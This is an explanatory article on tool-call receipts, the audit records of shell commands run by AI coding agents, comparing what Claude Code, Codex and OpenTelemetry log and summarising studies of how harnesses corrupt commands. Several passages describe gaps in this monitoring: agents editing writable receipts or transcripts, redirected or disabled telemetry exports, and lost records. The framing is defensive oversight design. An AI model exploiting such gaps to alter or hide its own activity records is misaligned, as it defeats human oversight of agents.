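# Tool-call receipts for AI agents: recording commands, environments, network targets, exit codes and artifacts

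## What a tool-call receipt is

A tool-call receipt is a structured record of one action that an AI agent took on a computer. An agent here is a language model that works on a task by repeatedly requesting actions and reading their results. Each request, such as listing a folder, opening a file or running tests, is a tool call. For a shell command (a line of text that tells the machine to run a program), the receipt records the command, the folder it ran in, the settings it inherited, the machines it contacted, how it ended and what it produced. Agents may work unattended for hours, and someone may later need the receipts to find out why the build broke or whether a password left the machine.

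The term "tool-call receipt" is recent and has no settled definition. *XAIP Receipts* (2026), an individual draft that the IETF, an internet standards body, hosts but does not endorse, defines a receipt as "a signed record of a single Tool execution attempt". The word "attempt" is apt because a failed call needs a record at least as much as a successful one. Signing is less essential, since an unsigned record works for someone debugging their own agent.

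### From request to result

Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes how the model emits a structured request, ordinary software rather than the model carries it out, and the result goes back into the conversation. This software is called a harness, and examples for programming work include Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. A harness gives the model a list of available tools, executes each request, appends the result to the text so far and queries the model again, until the model produces a message with no tool call.

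*Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, by OpenAI's Michael Bolin (2026), shows a model's request to run a tool. The request names the tool `shell`, the command `cat README.md`, the folder `/Users/mbolin/code/codex5` and an identifier for the call. `cat` prints a file's contents, so this command would read the project's introductory page. Some formats allow requests to include more fields. The sample code for OpenAI's local shell tool also reads a time limit, a user account and environment variables from the request.

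A harness typically passes the command text to a shell, such as Bash or PowerShell, which interprets command lines. The shell splits the line into a program name and its arguments, finds the program and asks the operating system to start it as a process, which is a running program with its own memory. The command can change at any of the five hand-overs that Yang, Li and colleagues (2026) count in *Do Tool Calls Execute as Intended?*, an October preprint: the harness packages the request, a wrapper passes it to the shell, the shell parses it, the operating system delivers the arguments, and the program parses them again.

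The new process inherits its working directory and environment from its parent, and the command text shows neither. According to the Linux man-pages' *path_resolution(7)*, the system looks up any path that does not begin with a slash starting from the working directory, so `README.md` refers to one file in `codex5` and to a different file, or none, one folder up. The environment is a list of `name=value` strings, according to the Linux man-pages' *environ(7)*. The variable `PATH` lists the folders in which the shell searches for programs, so if it is altered, `cat` can start a different program. The environment also often contains passwords and access keys, which makes it the most awkward part of a receipt to store.

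Harnesses differ in how much state they carry over from one command to the next. According to Anthropic's reference for Claude Code's tools, each Bash command runs in a separate process. In the main session, a change of directory carries over as long as it stays within the permitted directories, but variables set by a command do not. Anthropic's *Bash tool*, written for developers who build their own harness, has the application keep a single Bash process running, so both persist. The same two commands in the same order can therefore do different things in the two setups. A receipt has to record each call's actual directory and environment, because a reader cannot reliably infer them from the earlier commands.

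While it runs, `cat` writes the file's text to standard output and any error messages to standard error. When it ends, the process returns an exit code from 0 to 255. Zero means success by convention, and the GNU Project's *Exit Status* lists some of the other codes Bash uses: 127 for a command it could not find, 126 for a file it found but could not execute, and 128 plus the signal number for a process killed by a fatal signal. When a line holds several commands, Bash returns the status of the last one, so `cat README.md; echo done` returns 0 even if `README.md` does not exist.

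The harness then collects all this for the model. Microsoft's *Use the shell tool with the Azure OpenAI Responses API* shows a typical pair of items, a `shell_call` with the commands and a time limit, and a `shell_call_output` with standard output, standard error and the exit code. Its sample executor keeps those three values and records whether the command timed out. This is enough for the model to choose its next step, but it gives little help to anyone investigating a week later, because the sample doesn't set a directory or an environment (the process inherits the executor's) and doesn't check what the command changed on disk.

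### Digests, keyed fingerprints and signatures

Cryptography helps receipts refer to things that are too large or too sensitive to copy in, as they often must, and helps readers check whether anyone has edited a receipt since it was made.

A digest is a short, fixed-length value that a hash function computes from data. SHA-256, the usual choice, produces 256 bits, usually written as 64 hexadecimal characters. The same data always gives the same digest, altered data gives a different one, and nobody knows a practical way to make two different files with the same digest. A receipt can therefore identify an exact version of a very large file in one line. But computing a digest requires no secret, so anyone who rewrites a record can also compute a new digest to match.

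A keyed fingerprint, or HMAC, closes that gap by mixing a secret key into the computation, so that only someone with the key can produce the value. But checking the value requires the same key, so anyone who can check a record can also forge one. A public-key signature uses a pair of keys instead. The signer keeps one private and publishes the other, which lets outsiders verify a record without being able to forge one. Either method can validate a false record, because neither checks whether the content was true to begin with.

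*Tool Receipts, Not Zero-Knowledge Proofs* (2026), a preprint about an agent system called NabaOS, shows how these parts fit together. Its sample receipt, for an email search, holds an identifier, the tool's name, a digest of the inputs, a digest of the raw output, the number of results, the sender and subject of a message, a timestamp, a duration and an HMAC. The HMAC covers only the identifier, the tool's name, the two digests and the timestamp. Anyone who kept the raw output could recompute the number of results and the message details, but nothing protects the duration. It helps to check which fields a signature covers before relying on the others.

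### Summary, transcript, trace and receipt

A run usually leaves several records, and people confuse them. Most users read the model's own summary. Bolin's example of a closing message is "I added the architecture.md you asked for". The model generated that sentence the same way it generates all its other text, and nothing in the basic loop checks it against the disk. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works, sorts the links in an agent's record by whether the runtime emitted them, a person or model inferred them afterwards, or the agent reported them itself. It rates self-reports the weakest and includes the model's stated reasoning among them, because that reasoning is also text from the model and not an observation of the computation behind the answer.

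The transcript is the stored sequence of prompts, model outputs, tool calls and results. Claude Code writes it to a plain text file on the user's machine, according to Anthropic's *How Claude Code works*. Research papers tend to call it a "trajectory", whose definition in the glossary of *Reining in an Agentic Harness for High Energy Physics* (2026) includes errors, retries and human interventions. A transcript is the best source on how a run got from one step to the next. It contains the request as the model wrote it and the text that came back but, as Yang and colleagues point out, not what each stage in between received. The physics glossary uses "trial record" for a larger bundle that adds software versions, the configuration actually used and how the run ended, so that researchers can tell a scientific failure from an infrastructure fault.

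The conversation the model works from is an even poorer record. Bolin explains that Codex replaces the history with a shorter substitute once the history passes a size limit. Anthropic notes that in Claude Code, a parent agent that delegates work to a subagent sees only the subagent's final result, not its intermediate tool calls.

Timing traces come from monitoring ordinary server software. A trace consists of nested spans, which are named intervals with a start and an end. Anthropic's *Observability with OpenTelemetry* (OpenTelemetry is a widely used format for such data) describes the spans that Claude Code can export. By default they include durations, model names, tool names and usually token counts, but omit the content. A trace might therefore show that the Bash tool ran for forty seconds, but not which command it ran. An operator can switch on the command text, and even full inputs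 and outputs up to 60 KB, which brings the trace closer to a receipt. Even then, Claude Code sends spans in batches and can lose some if the receiving server is slow or the process is killed. Lost spans hardly matter on a latency chart, but an auditor cannot tell a lost span from a call that never happened.

A tool-call receipt covers a single call and should hold enough detail for a reader to judge that call by itself. It should show what the model requested, what ran and what changed. For `cat README.md`, the model requested that string, the program `cat` ran in a certain folder, and nothing changed. For `npm install`, which fetches the libraries of a JavaScript project, the request is only two words long, but it may run installation scripts written by strangers and change thousands of files.

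Yang and colleagues' definition of a command's action suits the second question well. It covers the executable, its arguments in order, the operators that join commands, the working directory, the relevant environment and the standard input (data fed to the program as it runs). Answering the third question requires checking the disk before and after the command, and using digests or a Git commit (the identifier of a saved version of the code) to identify the result exactly. The sample NabaOS receipt has no field for changes, which is adequate for an email search but not for a coding agent.

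### Who writes the record

Receipts written by the model would not expose its false reports, because a model that wrongly reports passing tests would also write a receipt for passing tests. In NabaOS, the runtime executes the call, writes and stores the receipt, and gives the model only the output and the receipt's identifier. The model never has the key. A reader or a simple program can then catch a summary that cites a receipt the runtime never issued. This assumes that the agent cannot reach the key or the stored receipts. A coding agent with shell access often runs commands with the user's permissions, and unless a sandbox (a restricted area for running programs) prevents it, those commands can edit files in the user's home folder, including transcripts.

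If the harness records the receipts, its operator controls the evidence. In an individual Internet-Draft on agent action receipts, Sahu objects that the party whose conduct is in question writes the existing logs and can change them. Wang and colleagues reviewed descriptions of monitoring and provenance systems and found none that reported tamper-evidence, signing or attestation for their traces. A team debugging its own agent can mostly ignore this problem, but it may be the main one for a customer or a regulator. One response is a hash chain, in which each record includes the digest of the previous one.

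Computers kept records of this kind about people and scripts long before agents existed. When Unix process accounting is on, the kernel (the core of the operating system) writes a record as each process terminates, according to the Linux man-pages' *acct(5)*. The structure in OpenBSD's *ACCT(5)* has ten bytes for the command's name, followed by processor time, elapsed time and starting time. Debian's *acct.5* adds that the feature began on BSD, an early branch of Unix, and that its details still vary between systems. Because the kernel writes the record, a program cannot leave itself out, and receipts are meant to have the same property. But the ten-byte field holds only the command's name, not its arguments, and a server that an agent started and left running has no record until it stops.

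Build servers, which compile and test code automatically, keep the output and exit code of each scripted step. A person wrote the script beforehand, so anyone can compare the log with it. An agent composes its commands as it runs, so the record also has to include each command it requested.

### The limit of the observer

A record contains only what the program making it could observe. A harness that starts a shell can record the text it sent, the two output channels and the exit code, but not the further processes that the shell starts or their network connections. For example, Anthropic documents that on Linux, a user can cap the memory available to Claude Code's commands. When the commands cannot stay under the cap, the kernel kills one, and nothing in that command's result mentions the cap. A receipt built from that result would be accurate but would omit the cause. The operator's harness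 can record even less about tools that run on the model provider's own servers, such as web search, because it receives only the provider's report of what ran.

Monitoring in the kernel can record processes and connections, but not which request they served. Matching them to a request requires an identifier passed with the command. Claude Code's tracing passes one to each shell command in an environment variable, `TRACEPARENT`. According to Anthropic, a program that emits its own spans can use this variable to attach them to the right tool call. A program that ignores the variable still runs, but its activity doesn't appear under that call.

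## What each field should hold: published formats and product documentation

Neither Claude Code nor Codex exports a record with every field a later reader would want, so the receipt below is an illustration with invented values. In the example, an agent is preparing a web shop's code for a machine without internet access. It requests `pip download requests==2.32.3 -d wheels`, which tells pip, Python's package installer, to download version 2.32.3 of the `requests` library into the folder `wheels`. The harness runs the command in `/work/shop`. Pip fetches packages from the company's own server, called a package index. It reads the server's address, which contains a username and password, from the environment variable `PIP_INDEX_URL`.

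```json
{
  "run_id": "run-7f3a",
  "call_id": "call-0042",
  "agent_id": "dependency-worker",
  "parent_agent_id": "main",
  "requested": {
    "tool": "shell",
    "command": "pip download requests==2.32.3 -d wheels",
    "timeout_ms": 120000
  },
  "approval": {
    "decision": "accept",
    "source": "user_temporary",
    "rewritten_command": null
  },
  "ran": {
    "shell": "/usr/bin/bash",
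    "shell_version": "5.2.21",
    "executable": "/usr/bin/python3.12",
    "argv": ["/work/shop/.venv/bin/python3", "/work/shop/.venv/bin/pip",
             "download", "requests==2.32.3", "-d", "wheels"],
    "cwd": "/work/shop",
    "git_commit": "4be1c09d7a52f3e86b0d94c17fa2e5380c6d9b71",
    "uncommitted": {
      "changed": ["requirements.txt"],
      "untracked": [],
      "patch_sha256": "b81f…"
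    },
    "env": {
      "PATH": "/work/shop/.venv/bin:/usr/bin:/bin",
      "PIP_INDEX_URL": "https://ci:[REDACTED]@pypi.example.com/simple"
    },
    "env_names_only": ["HOME", "LANG", "USER"]
  },
  "network": [
    {"host": "pypi.example.com", "address": "203.0.113.20",
     "port": 443, "protocol": "tcp", "seen_by": "proxy"},
    {"host": "files.example.com", "address": "203.0.113.31",
     "port": 443, "protocol": "tcp", "seen_by": "proxy"}
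  ],
  "outcome": {"status": "exited", "exit_code": 0, "signal": null},
  "output": {
    "stdout": {"bytes": 1912, "sha256": "0c7e…",
               "stored_bytes": 1912, "truncated": false},
    "stderr": {"bytes": 0, "sha256": "e3b0…",
               "stored_bytes": 0, "truncated": false}
  },
  "times": {
    "requested_at": "2026-10-05T09:14:02.310Z",
    "started_at": "2026-10-05T09:14:20.655Z",
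    "ended_at": "2026-10-05T09:14:23.871Z",
    "duration_ms": 3216
  },
  "artifacts": [
    {"path": "wheels/requests-2.32.3-py3-none-any.whl", "sha256": "51d2…"},
    {"path": "wheels/certifi-2025.1.31-py3-none-any.whl", "sha256": "a90c…"},
    {"path": "wheels/charset_normalizer-3.4.1-py3-none-any.whl", "sha256": "77be…"},
    {"path": "wheels/idna-3.10-py3-none-any.whl", "sha256": "1f46…"},
    {"path": "wheels/urllib3-2.3.0-py3-none-any.whl", "sha256": "e8a3…"}
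  ]
}
```

An ellipsis stands for the rest of a digest.

### The command and the place it ran

`requested.command` holds the text exactly as the model emitted it. `argv`, the conventional name for a process's argument list, holds what the program received. The two differ even for this harmless command because `pip` on Linux is a short Python script, which the operating system runs by starting Python and passing it the script's path. The harness started only Bash, so recording `argv` requires an observer that can see the processes Bash starts. A line that joins several commands needs one list per process.

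Semantic conventions are agreed names and meanings for monitoring data, which let tools from different vendors read the same records. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for CLI (command line interface) programs* defines the argument list the same way, "as received by the process". It recommends naming the span after the executable file, so the example would appear as `python3.12`, and a search for `pip` would find it only through the arguments. But OpenTelemetry advises against collecting arguments by default unless sensitive data is removed first.

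The shell and its version matter because shells can split the same command text differently. For example, PowerShell 7 accepts `&&` between two commands, while the older Windows PowerShell 5.1 rejects the whole line as a syntax error. An investigator who reruns a command in the wrong shell may see a failure the agent never had, or miss one it did.

`cwd` is the absolute path of the working directory, so the relative path `wheels` resolves to `/work/shop/wheels`. The Git commit identifies the version of the project that the command could read. Agents usually edit files before they commit, so the files on disk often differ from that commit. The receipt therefore also lists the changed files and gives the digest of a patch (a text file of the differences) that the harness stores elsewhere. Ordinary `git diff` output leaves out files that Git doesn't track yet, so these need their own list. The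 Git state can determine the result of a test command, but it hardly matters for this `pip` command, which reads none of the project's files.

`env` shows which settings influenced the command. `PATH` determined which copy of `pip` ran, and `PIP_INDEX_URL` determined where the packages came from. Without that address, a reader would probably assume they came from the public Python index. `PIP_INDEX_URL` is therefore the variable a reader most needs, but it contains a password, so the harness replaces only the password before it stores the record. For variables that are unlikely to matter, recording the names is enough.

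The values have to come from the command's own environment, because harnesses don't always pass on all their variables. Claude Code withholds all variables that begin with `OTEL_` from the processes it starts, according to Anthropic's *Monitoring*. Codex's `shell_environment_policy` setting, described in OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration*, can start from a full, reduced or empty set of variables, remove some by pattern (such as `AWS_*`) and add others. A receipt that copied the harness's environment could list credentials that the command never received.

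### Connections, output and files

The command doesn't specify a host and the environment specifies only one, but pip contacted two, because an index page can link to files on another server, as the pages of the public Python index do. The `network` field therefore has to come from a tool that monitored the connections, in this case a proxy, which is identified in `seen_by`. An empty list means that the monitor detected no connections. If there was no monitor, the field should be `null`, so that readers don't mistake missing data for evidence that the command stayed offline.

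For each output channel, the receipt records the length and digest of the full output and the number of bytes the harness stored. The harness computes the digest before truncating anything, so anyone with a complete copy can check it against the digest later. Truncation is common. For example, Claude Code cuts values over 512 characters when it exports tool arguments and limits the whole set to about 4,000. Test programs usually print their summary of failures last, so keeping only the beginning of the output loses the most useful lines.

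`artifacts` lists the files the command left behind. The command named only `requests`, but pip also downloaded its four dependencies, and neither the command nor an exit code of 0 shows which versions arrived. The digests let someone check a year later whether a suspect file on a server is one of these five. A later section explains how harnesses and outside observers obtain file digests and network targets.

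### How the call ended

An exit code exists only for a process that ran and ended, so the receipt needs a separate `status`.

| What happened | `status` | `exit_code` | `signal` |
|---|---|---|---|
| The command ended by itself | `exited` | the number it returned | `null` |
| The kernel or a user killed it | `signaled` | `null` | for example `SIGKILL` |
| The harness stopped it at the time limit | `timed_out` | `null` | the signal the harness sent |
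| It was still running when the harness answered the model | `running` | `null` | `null` |
| A person or a rule refused it | `denied` | `null` | `null` |
| The harness could not start it | `not_started` | `null` | `null` |

Software libraries represent killed processes differently. Python's standard library returns −9 for a process killed by signal 9, while Node.js gives no exit code and names the signal separately. A harness that stores a missing exit code as 0 therefore records a killed command as successful. Bash returns 137 in the same case, but a program can also exit with 137 without being killed, so the receipt should name the signal whenever the observer has that information.

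For commands that ended, the exit code is worth keeping alongside any success flag. OpenTelemetry requires the exit code and treats every value other than 0 as an error. But `grep`, which searches text, returns 1 when it finds no match and 2 when an error occurs, such as a missing file. Recording only "failed" would make a search with no matches look like an error.

OpenTelemetry intends these conventions for short-lived programs and excludes long-running background tasks, so they fit background commands badly. If an agent starts a development server in the background, the harness gets control back at once, and an exit code of 0 recorded then would describe only the launch. It is better to record `running` in the first receipt and write a second receipt with the same `call_id` once the server stops.

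"Timed out" can also refer to the approval. Codex can pass approval requests to a reviewer agent, and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* lists the possible results as approved, denied, aborted and timed out. If the review times out, the action doesn't run. That call belongs under `denied`, with the reason in `approval`, to distinguish it from a command that the harness stopped partway through, which may have changed files.

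Denied calls need receipts because they show what the agent tried to do. They also help explain what it did next. After a refused download, for example, an agent might write its own replacement for the library, which would look strange to anyone who didn't know about the refusal. If denials left no receipt, a gap in the numbering could mean either a refusal or a lost record.

### Identifiers, times and approval

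`run_id` groups the calls of one run, and `call_id` should be the identifier that the harness already uses for the model's request. According to Anthropic, Claude Code uses the same `tool_use_id` in log events, trace spans and the data passed to hooks, so an investigator can join all three. The agent identifiers show who delegated the work. Claude Code omits `agent_id` for the main session and `parent_agent_id` for subagents that the main session started. Because a reader can't tell a deliberately omitted value from a lost one, the example uses `main` instead.

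A receipt may also need to name a person. Claude Code attributes each action to the developer who started the session and exports their email address if they have signed in. With a plain API key, it exports only identifiers for the installation and the session, so Anthropic tells companies to add the user's identity themselves.

The three timestamps separate the wait for approval from the command's running time. In the example, the user took 18 seconds to approve the command and pip took 3 seconds to run. Claude Code's main span for a tool call includes both, and two smaller spans inside it time them separately. Someone looking for slow commands in the main spans would count the approval wait as part of pip's running time.

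Counters are less reliable than timestamps for ordering events. Claude Code numbers its events from 0 each time its process starts, so when a user resumes an old session, later events can carry lower numbers than earlier ones. Anthropic recommends sorting by timestamp and using the counter only to break ties.

The `approval` field records who allowed the call and whether they saw the command that ran. Claude Code lets a permission decision rewrite the request, so the command that ran may not be the one they saw. `requested.command` keeps the original text, and `rewritten_command` holds the new text if there is any.

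The example takes its `source` value from Claude Code, where `user_temporary` generally means a one-time "Yes". If the user chooses "Yes, and don't ask again", the event records `user_permanent`, but in the interactive program, later calls under the same rule record `config`. That value also covers project settings, company policy, command-line flags, inherently safe tools and failed permission prompts, and Anthropic notes that the event doesn't identify which of them applied. A security reviewer can therefore learn little more from `config` than that no person decided on the call at the time, so a better receipt would name the rule that applied.

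### What the products and conventions record

The table compares the example with the Claude Code events and spans that Anthropic lists, the Codex events that OpenAI describes, and OpenTelemetry's conventions. "Details switch" stands for `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS=1`. Neither Claude Code nor Codex exports these events by default.

| Part of the receipt | Claude Code | Codex | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|---|
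| Command as requested | With the details switch | Not listed | Tool-call details, since version 1.38 |
| Arguments as received | No | Not listed | Recommended, but not by default without sanitization |
| Shell and version | Tool name only | Tool name, in metrics | Executable name required, path recommended |
| Working directory | No | Not listed | Recommended for processes, absent from the command span |
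| Git state | Commit and branch after a successful `git commit`, with the details switch | Not listed | Absent from the command span |
| Environment | No | Not listed | Absent from the command span |
| Network target | No | Not listed | Absent from the command span |
| Exit code | Success flag and error category | Success flag | Required |
| Output | Size; text with a further switch | Snippet | Absent from the command span |
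| Times | Timestamp and duration | Duration | Start and end of the span |
| Identifiers | Session and call; agents in traces | Conversation | Process number and tool-call identifier |
| Approval | Decision and source | Decision and source | Absent from the command span |
| Files produced | Only the Git commit above | Not listed | Absent from the command span |

A field marked "not listed" may still be present in the event, unlike one marked "no". OpenAI calls its list of events representative and describes each event in one line. The line for `codex.tool_result` lists duration, success and an output snippet. OpenAI refers readers to the code repository for the full catalogue.

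Neither product documents any of a receipt's six main facts (command, working directory, environment, network targets, exit code and artifacts) as part of its default export. Without further switches, Claude Code's spans show the tool name and duration, and its events add whether the call succeeded and the size of its result. If tracing is also on, versions from 2.1.268 add the name of the command's first program if it is on a fixed list that includes `git` and `npm`.

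The details switch adds the full command and, for commits, the Git identifier. Working directory, environment, network target and exit code still have no field of their own. A failed command gets an error category such as `ShellError`, so a missing program (exit code 127) and a failed test (often 1) may look alike unless the error message contains the exit code.

OpenTelemetry's process conventions fill some of these gaps. They require the exit code and recommend recording the working directory and parent process as process attributes. The span for a command records neither its environment nor its network connections.

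These conventions are still changing. OpenTelemetry marks its command conventions as "Development", although the attributes for exit code, process number and arguments are release candidates, which are close to final. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, which covers calls to models, also has "Development" status. According to a version history by the software vendor Greptime (2026), version 1.38 added tool definitions and call details, and version 1.41 required the name of each `execute_tool` span to include the tool's name. A receipt that borrows these names should record the version it follows, because a search written for one version may miss records from the next.

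### Switches and export destinations

In Claude Code, `CLAUDE_CODE_ENABLE_TELEMETRY=1` turns telemetry on, and the operator chooses separate exporters for metrics (counts and totals), log events and traces. The log events most relevant to receipts are `tool_decision`, which records each permission decision, and `tool_result`, which records each call that ran. A rejected call produces only a `tool_decision` event. Without the details switch, the event for a rejected Bash call includes the tool name but not the command, so a refused attempt to read a private key looks the same as a refused `ls`.

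With the details switch on, both events include the full command, the time limit, and whether the model asked to run outside the sandbox. File paths and web addresses in a tool's input appear only in `tool_result`, so when a person refuses a file edit, the operator can see the refusal but not which file the edit would have changed.

Another switch, `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_CONTENT=1`, adds tool inputs and outputs to traces, and `OTEL_LOG_RAW_API_BODIES` exports every exchange with the model, including the whole conversation so far. None of these switches removes secrets. Anthropic warns that arguments may contain sensitive values and leaves the company running the agent to filter them in its own monitoring system. If the agent had typed the index address into the `pip` command, the details switch would have exported the password.

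Codex's export settings are in the `[otel]` block, and the exporter is `none` by default. OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* lists one content switch, `log_user_prompt`, for the user's prompts, and none for the output snippet in `codex.tool_result`. A team that turns on export should therefore expect to receive some of what commands print.

These events are off by default, but OpenAI collects anonymous usage metrics unless a separate setting disables them. The tool-call metrics count calls by tool and result and omit the shell command.

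An export is only useful as evidence if the developer, or an agent that can edit the developer's settings, can't redirect it. If an administrator's managed settings file for Claude Code sets `OTEL_EXPORTER_OTLP_ENDPOINT`, the address of the server that collects the data, Claude Code removes any competing addresses at startup. Before version 2.1.217, a developer could still redirect a single kind of data, such as logs, by setting a more specific variable.

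Even if the managed file fixes the export address, a developer's own settings can still disable logs or send them to the local screen. Anthropic therefore advises administrators to set the exporter in that file as well.

Codex ignores `[otel]` settings in a project's own configuration file and shows a warning, so a downloaded repository cannot redirect the telemetry. The user's personal configuration file can still set them. Administrators can enforce requirements through `requirements.toml`, but the keys OpenAI lists for that file cover approvals, sandboxing, network access and hooks, not telemetry. OpenAI also mentions other managed configuration layers, one of which may be able to lock the telemetry destination.

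Codex also sends its events in batches, so a killed run can lose the last ones, as in Claude Code.

### Transcripts and hooks on the developer's machine

Claude Code stores transcripts under `~/.claude/projects` whether or not telemetry is on, so the requested command is normally there even when the company's collector never receives it. By default, Claude Code deletes transcripts after 30 days. Anthropic warns that the format is internal and can change with any release, so a program that builds receipts from transcripts may stop working after an update.

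Codex can save transcripts to `history.jsonl`. The user can turn this off, limit the tokens stored for each tool output, or cap the file's size. If the file exceeds the cap, Codex drops the oldest entries first. In either product, the local copy may be gone if someone starts investigating a run weeks later.

Hooks are a more direct way to produce receipts. A hook is a script that the harness runs at a fixed point, such as just before a tool call (`PreToolUse`) or just after it (`PostToolUse`). OpenAI gives an example in which a Python script checks each Bash command before Codex runs it. A similar entry could call a script that writes receipts:

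```toml
[[hooks.PostToolUse]]
matcher = "^Bash$"

[[hooks.PostToolUse.hooks]]
type = "command"
command = '/usr/bin/python3 /opt/receipts/write.py'
timeout = 30
```

A receipt writer works best with two hooks. The first saves the request, the time and the Git state, and the second adds the outcome. If the harness crashes in between, the first record still shows that a call was under way. In Claude Code, a `PreToolUse` hook can allow or refuse a call, so it runs before the decision and can record requests that someone then refuses.

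A hook can't supply every field. It runs as a separate process, so it reads its own environment, which may differ from the command's, and it can't observe the command's network connections.

Both vendors provide ways to make sure such hooks run. Administrators can install managed hooks in Codex and set `allow_managed_hooks_only`, which makes Codex skip user, project and plugin hooks. Claude Code exports an event for each configured hook when a session starts. After the hooks for an event finish, it also exports how many succeeded and how many failed without stopping the call, so a company can notice when its receipt script has crashed and the agent has carried on.

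In its default mode, the Codex sandbox lets commands write to the project folder and to temporary folders such as `/tmp`, so the agent could change any receipts the script saves there. Sending each receipt to another machine avoids this. In Claude Code, the script then needs its own copy of the collector's address, because hooks don't receive the `OTEL_` variables either.

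## Whether the command and exit code can be trusted: controlled tests and production logs

A hook or a log event copies the command text and the exit code from the harness. The text may differ from what the program received, and the exit code may be 0 even though the program did nothing. Two preprints from late 2026, both led by Boyang Yang of Yanshan University, measured these problems. In October, Yang and colleagues compared the commands that models wrote with what shells and programs received. In November, *RECEIPT* (Yang, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested what commands do when they prompt for input and receive none. Each preprint also presents a repair that its own team built and deployed in a commercial product, so results from other groups matter more here.

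### How a command changes on its way to the program

The October preprint defines "intent-execution correspondence" as a match between the action the machine executes and the action the model's text specifies under the tool's rules. "Intent" here means the model's text, not the user's goal. If the model writes a command that is wrong for its shell and the command reaches the shell unchanged, the mistake is the model's.

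The preprint calls the five hand-overs between the harness and the program "hops": tool serialization, the host wrapper (a longer command line that starts the shell), the shell parse, the process interface and the target parser. The process interface carries the arguments from the shell to the program. Linux passes them as a list, but Windows passes a single string that the program has to split again.

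Yang and colleagues describe four ways in which a hop alters a call. In quote consumption, a program parses text a second time and strips the quotes, so `console.log("test")` arrives as `console.log(test)`, which prints the variable `test` instead of the word. In re-expansion, a receiver treats plain text as an instruction; for example, interactive Bash can replace `!x` with an earlier command. In truncation, part of the text disappears. Git Bash, the Windows version of Bash that comes with Git, cuts a quoted argument after 8,186 units of text (roughly, characters) and turns each pair of backslashes into one. The older Windows interpreter `cmd.exe` ends a command at its first line break. In an arity change, an argument goes missing or splits in two.

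Merged backslashes are easy to miss. If an agent writes a Python file containing the path `"C:\\new"` and the path arrives as `"C:\new"`, Python reads `\n` as a line break. The command that wrote the file still succeeds, and the fault appears only when a program later tries to open the path.

To find such changes in old sessions, the researchers needed to know what each hop had received, but rerunning recorded commands could delete files or publish code. They built probes, called witnesses, that start the shell as the harness would but report what it received instead of running it. For Bash, the witness uses `BASH_ENV`, a variable naming a file that Bash reads before it executes a command string. The code in that file reports the string and ends the process, so the command never runs. For the process interface, a small program replaces the real one and records the arguments it receives. For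 PowerShell, the witness computes the script that PowerShell would execute and parses it without running it.

Comparing the sent and received texts character by character would give false alarms because, for example, Bash treats `a\b` and `a\\b` as the same word inside double quotes. The researchers instead ran both texts through the receiver's own parser and counted a change only if the resulting actions differed. In a sample that two people labelled by hand, this method matched their labels on all 115 pairs, whereas plain text comparison wrongly flagged 15 of the 35 pairs they had labelled unchanged.

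### What happened in 47,828 production calls

The main data come from six developers at one company, who used Claude Code and Codex on Windows for 11 weeks. Their 261 sessions contain 47,828 shell calls, and none of the sessions was set up for the study.

The headline rate covers only "exposed" calls, whose text a hop could plausibly damage. A Bash call counts as exposed if it contains a pair of backslashes, at least 1,000 characters, or a here-document (a block of text, often code, embedded in the command). Claude Code's Bash tool changed 902 of 7,491 exposed calls, or 12.0%. No other Bash call changed in the replay, so the rate across all 32,259 Bash calls is about 2.8%. The tool changed 67.0% of the calls with a backslash pair and every call of 8,000 characters or more.

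The developers installed the paper's repair partway through the period. Before that, 663 calls with altered backslashes ran, and 535 of them (80.7%) executed the wrong action without a reported error. All 11 truncated calls from the same period failed with an error. A separate problem at the process interface changed 297 of 4,491 exposed PowerShell calls (6.6%), mostly by dropping double quotes inside a value.

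These figures are a lower bound for this team because the replay used the shortest wrapper that the harness generates. Many sessions had longer wrappers, which cut off commands that the shortest one would have delivered whole.

### How far the rates depend on Windows

The 12.0% figure comes from Git Bash on Windows and doesn't apply to an ordinary Linux setup. When a Linux harness passes the command to Bash as an argument, Bash receives the text unchanged. Yang and colleagues found no changes in 4,012 calls by nine developers, in 161,214 Codex calls from outside contributors, or in 1,779 test calls across four harnesses.

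The rate also varies among Windows users. In sessions from two developers outside the company, 5 of 605 and 2 of 52 exposed calls changed, all without an error. The 12.0% therefore depends heavily on how six colleagues and their agents wrote commands.

Linux harnesses that process a command's text before Bash parses it do corrupt some commands. Terminus 2, a harness used for Terminal-Bench, types commands into an interactive terminal, where a tab triggers completion and an exclamation mark can recall an old command. In public runs, 245 batches of keystrokes contained one of these characters, and 186 of them changed when the researchers retyped them. They came from 137 of 4,356 scored runs. OpenHands and SWE-ReX, which escape or split commands before passing them on, also altered some commands.

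Yang and colleagues also report that all ten harnesses they measured changed at least one call. The evidence is thin for some harnesses, such as Gemini CLI and DeepSeek Harness, which each changed 2 of 20 test inputs that the researchers had filled with quotes, backslashes and line breaks. This test shows that damage can occur, but not how often users encounter it.

Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026), an unrelated group, had already isolated one cause on Linux. In *QuoteBench*, they had models write Bash commands for 56 small tasks and ran each reply both directly and inside an additional `bash -c "..."` without escaping the reply. Across eight model configurations, the extra layer lowered the success rate by 55.4 to 73.2 percentage points. Sending the replies through a real `ssh` connection gave almost identical losses, and correct escaping eliminated them. Commands for remote machines and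 containers often pass through such a layer, so they can still go wrong on Linux even when the local Bash receives the right text. Li and colleagues did not estimate how common unescaped layers are. No independent repeat of the production measurement is known.

### Why transcripts point to the wrong cause

An error message in a transcript refers to the command the shell received, which may differ from the one the model sent. In one test, 13 models tried to run a test file named `test_app (v2) & more.py` and correctly put the name in quotes. The harness's launch method stripped the quotes, and PowerShell returned an error about the ampersand. In the transcript, this looks like a quoting mistake by the model. The models also took it for their own mistake and rewrote their correct commands.

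In the production sessions, 426 calls ended in a Bash or Python parse error. Yang and colleagues traced 306 to the path, 84 to the model's text and 36 to another interpreter that the command had started.

They then tested whether a reader of the transcript could find the cause. Two people labelled a sample of failures with error messages and agreed on the cause of 102, of which 56 came from the path. The language model Qwen2.5-72B judged the same failures from the transcripts, using prompts from Who&When, a published method for finding the agent and step responsible for a failure. Given each whole transcript at once, it attributed 97 of the 102 failures (95.1%) to the agent's model and none to the path. With two other prompting methods, it identified 29 and 25 of the 56 path failures, but each time it also attributed 20 of the other 46 to the path, which is hardly better than chance. The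 witnesses identified 54 of the 56 and made one false attribution.

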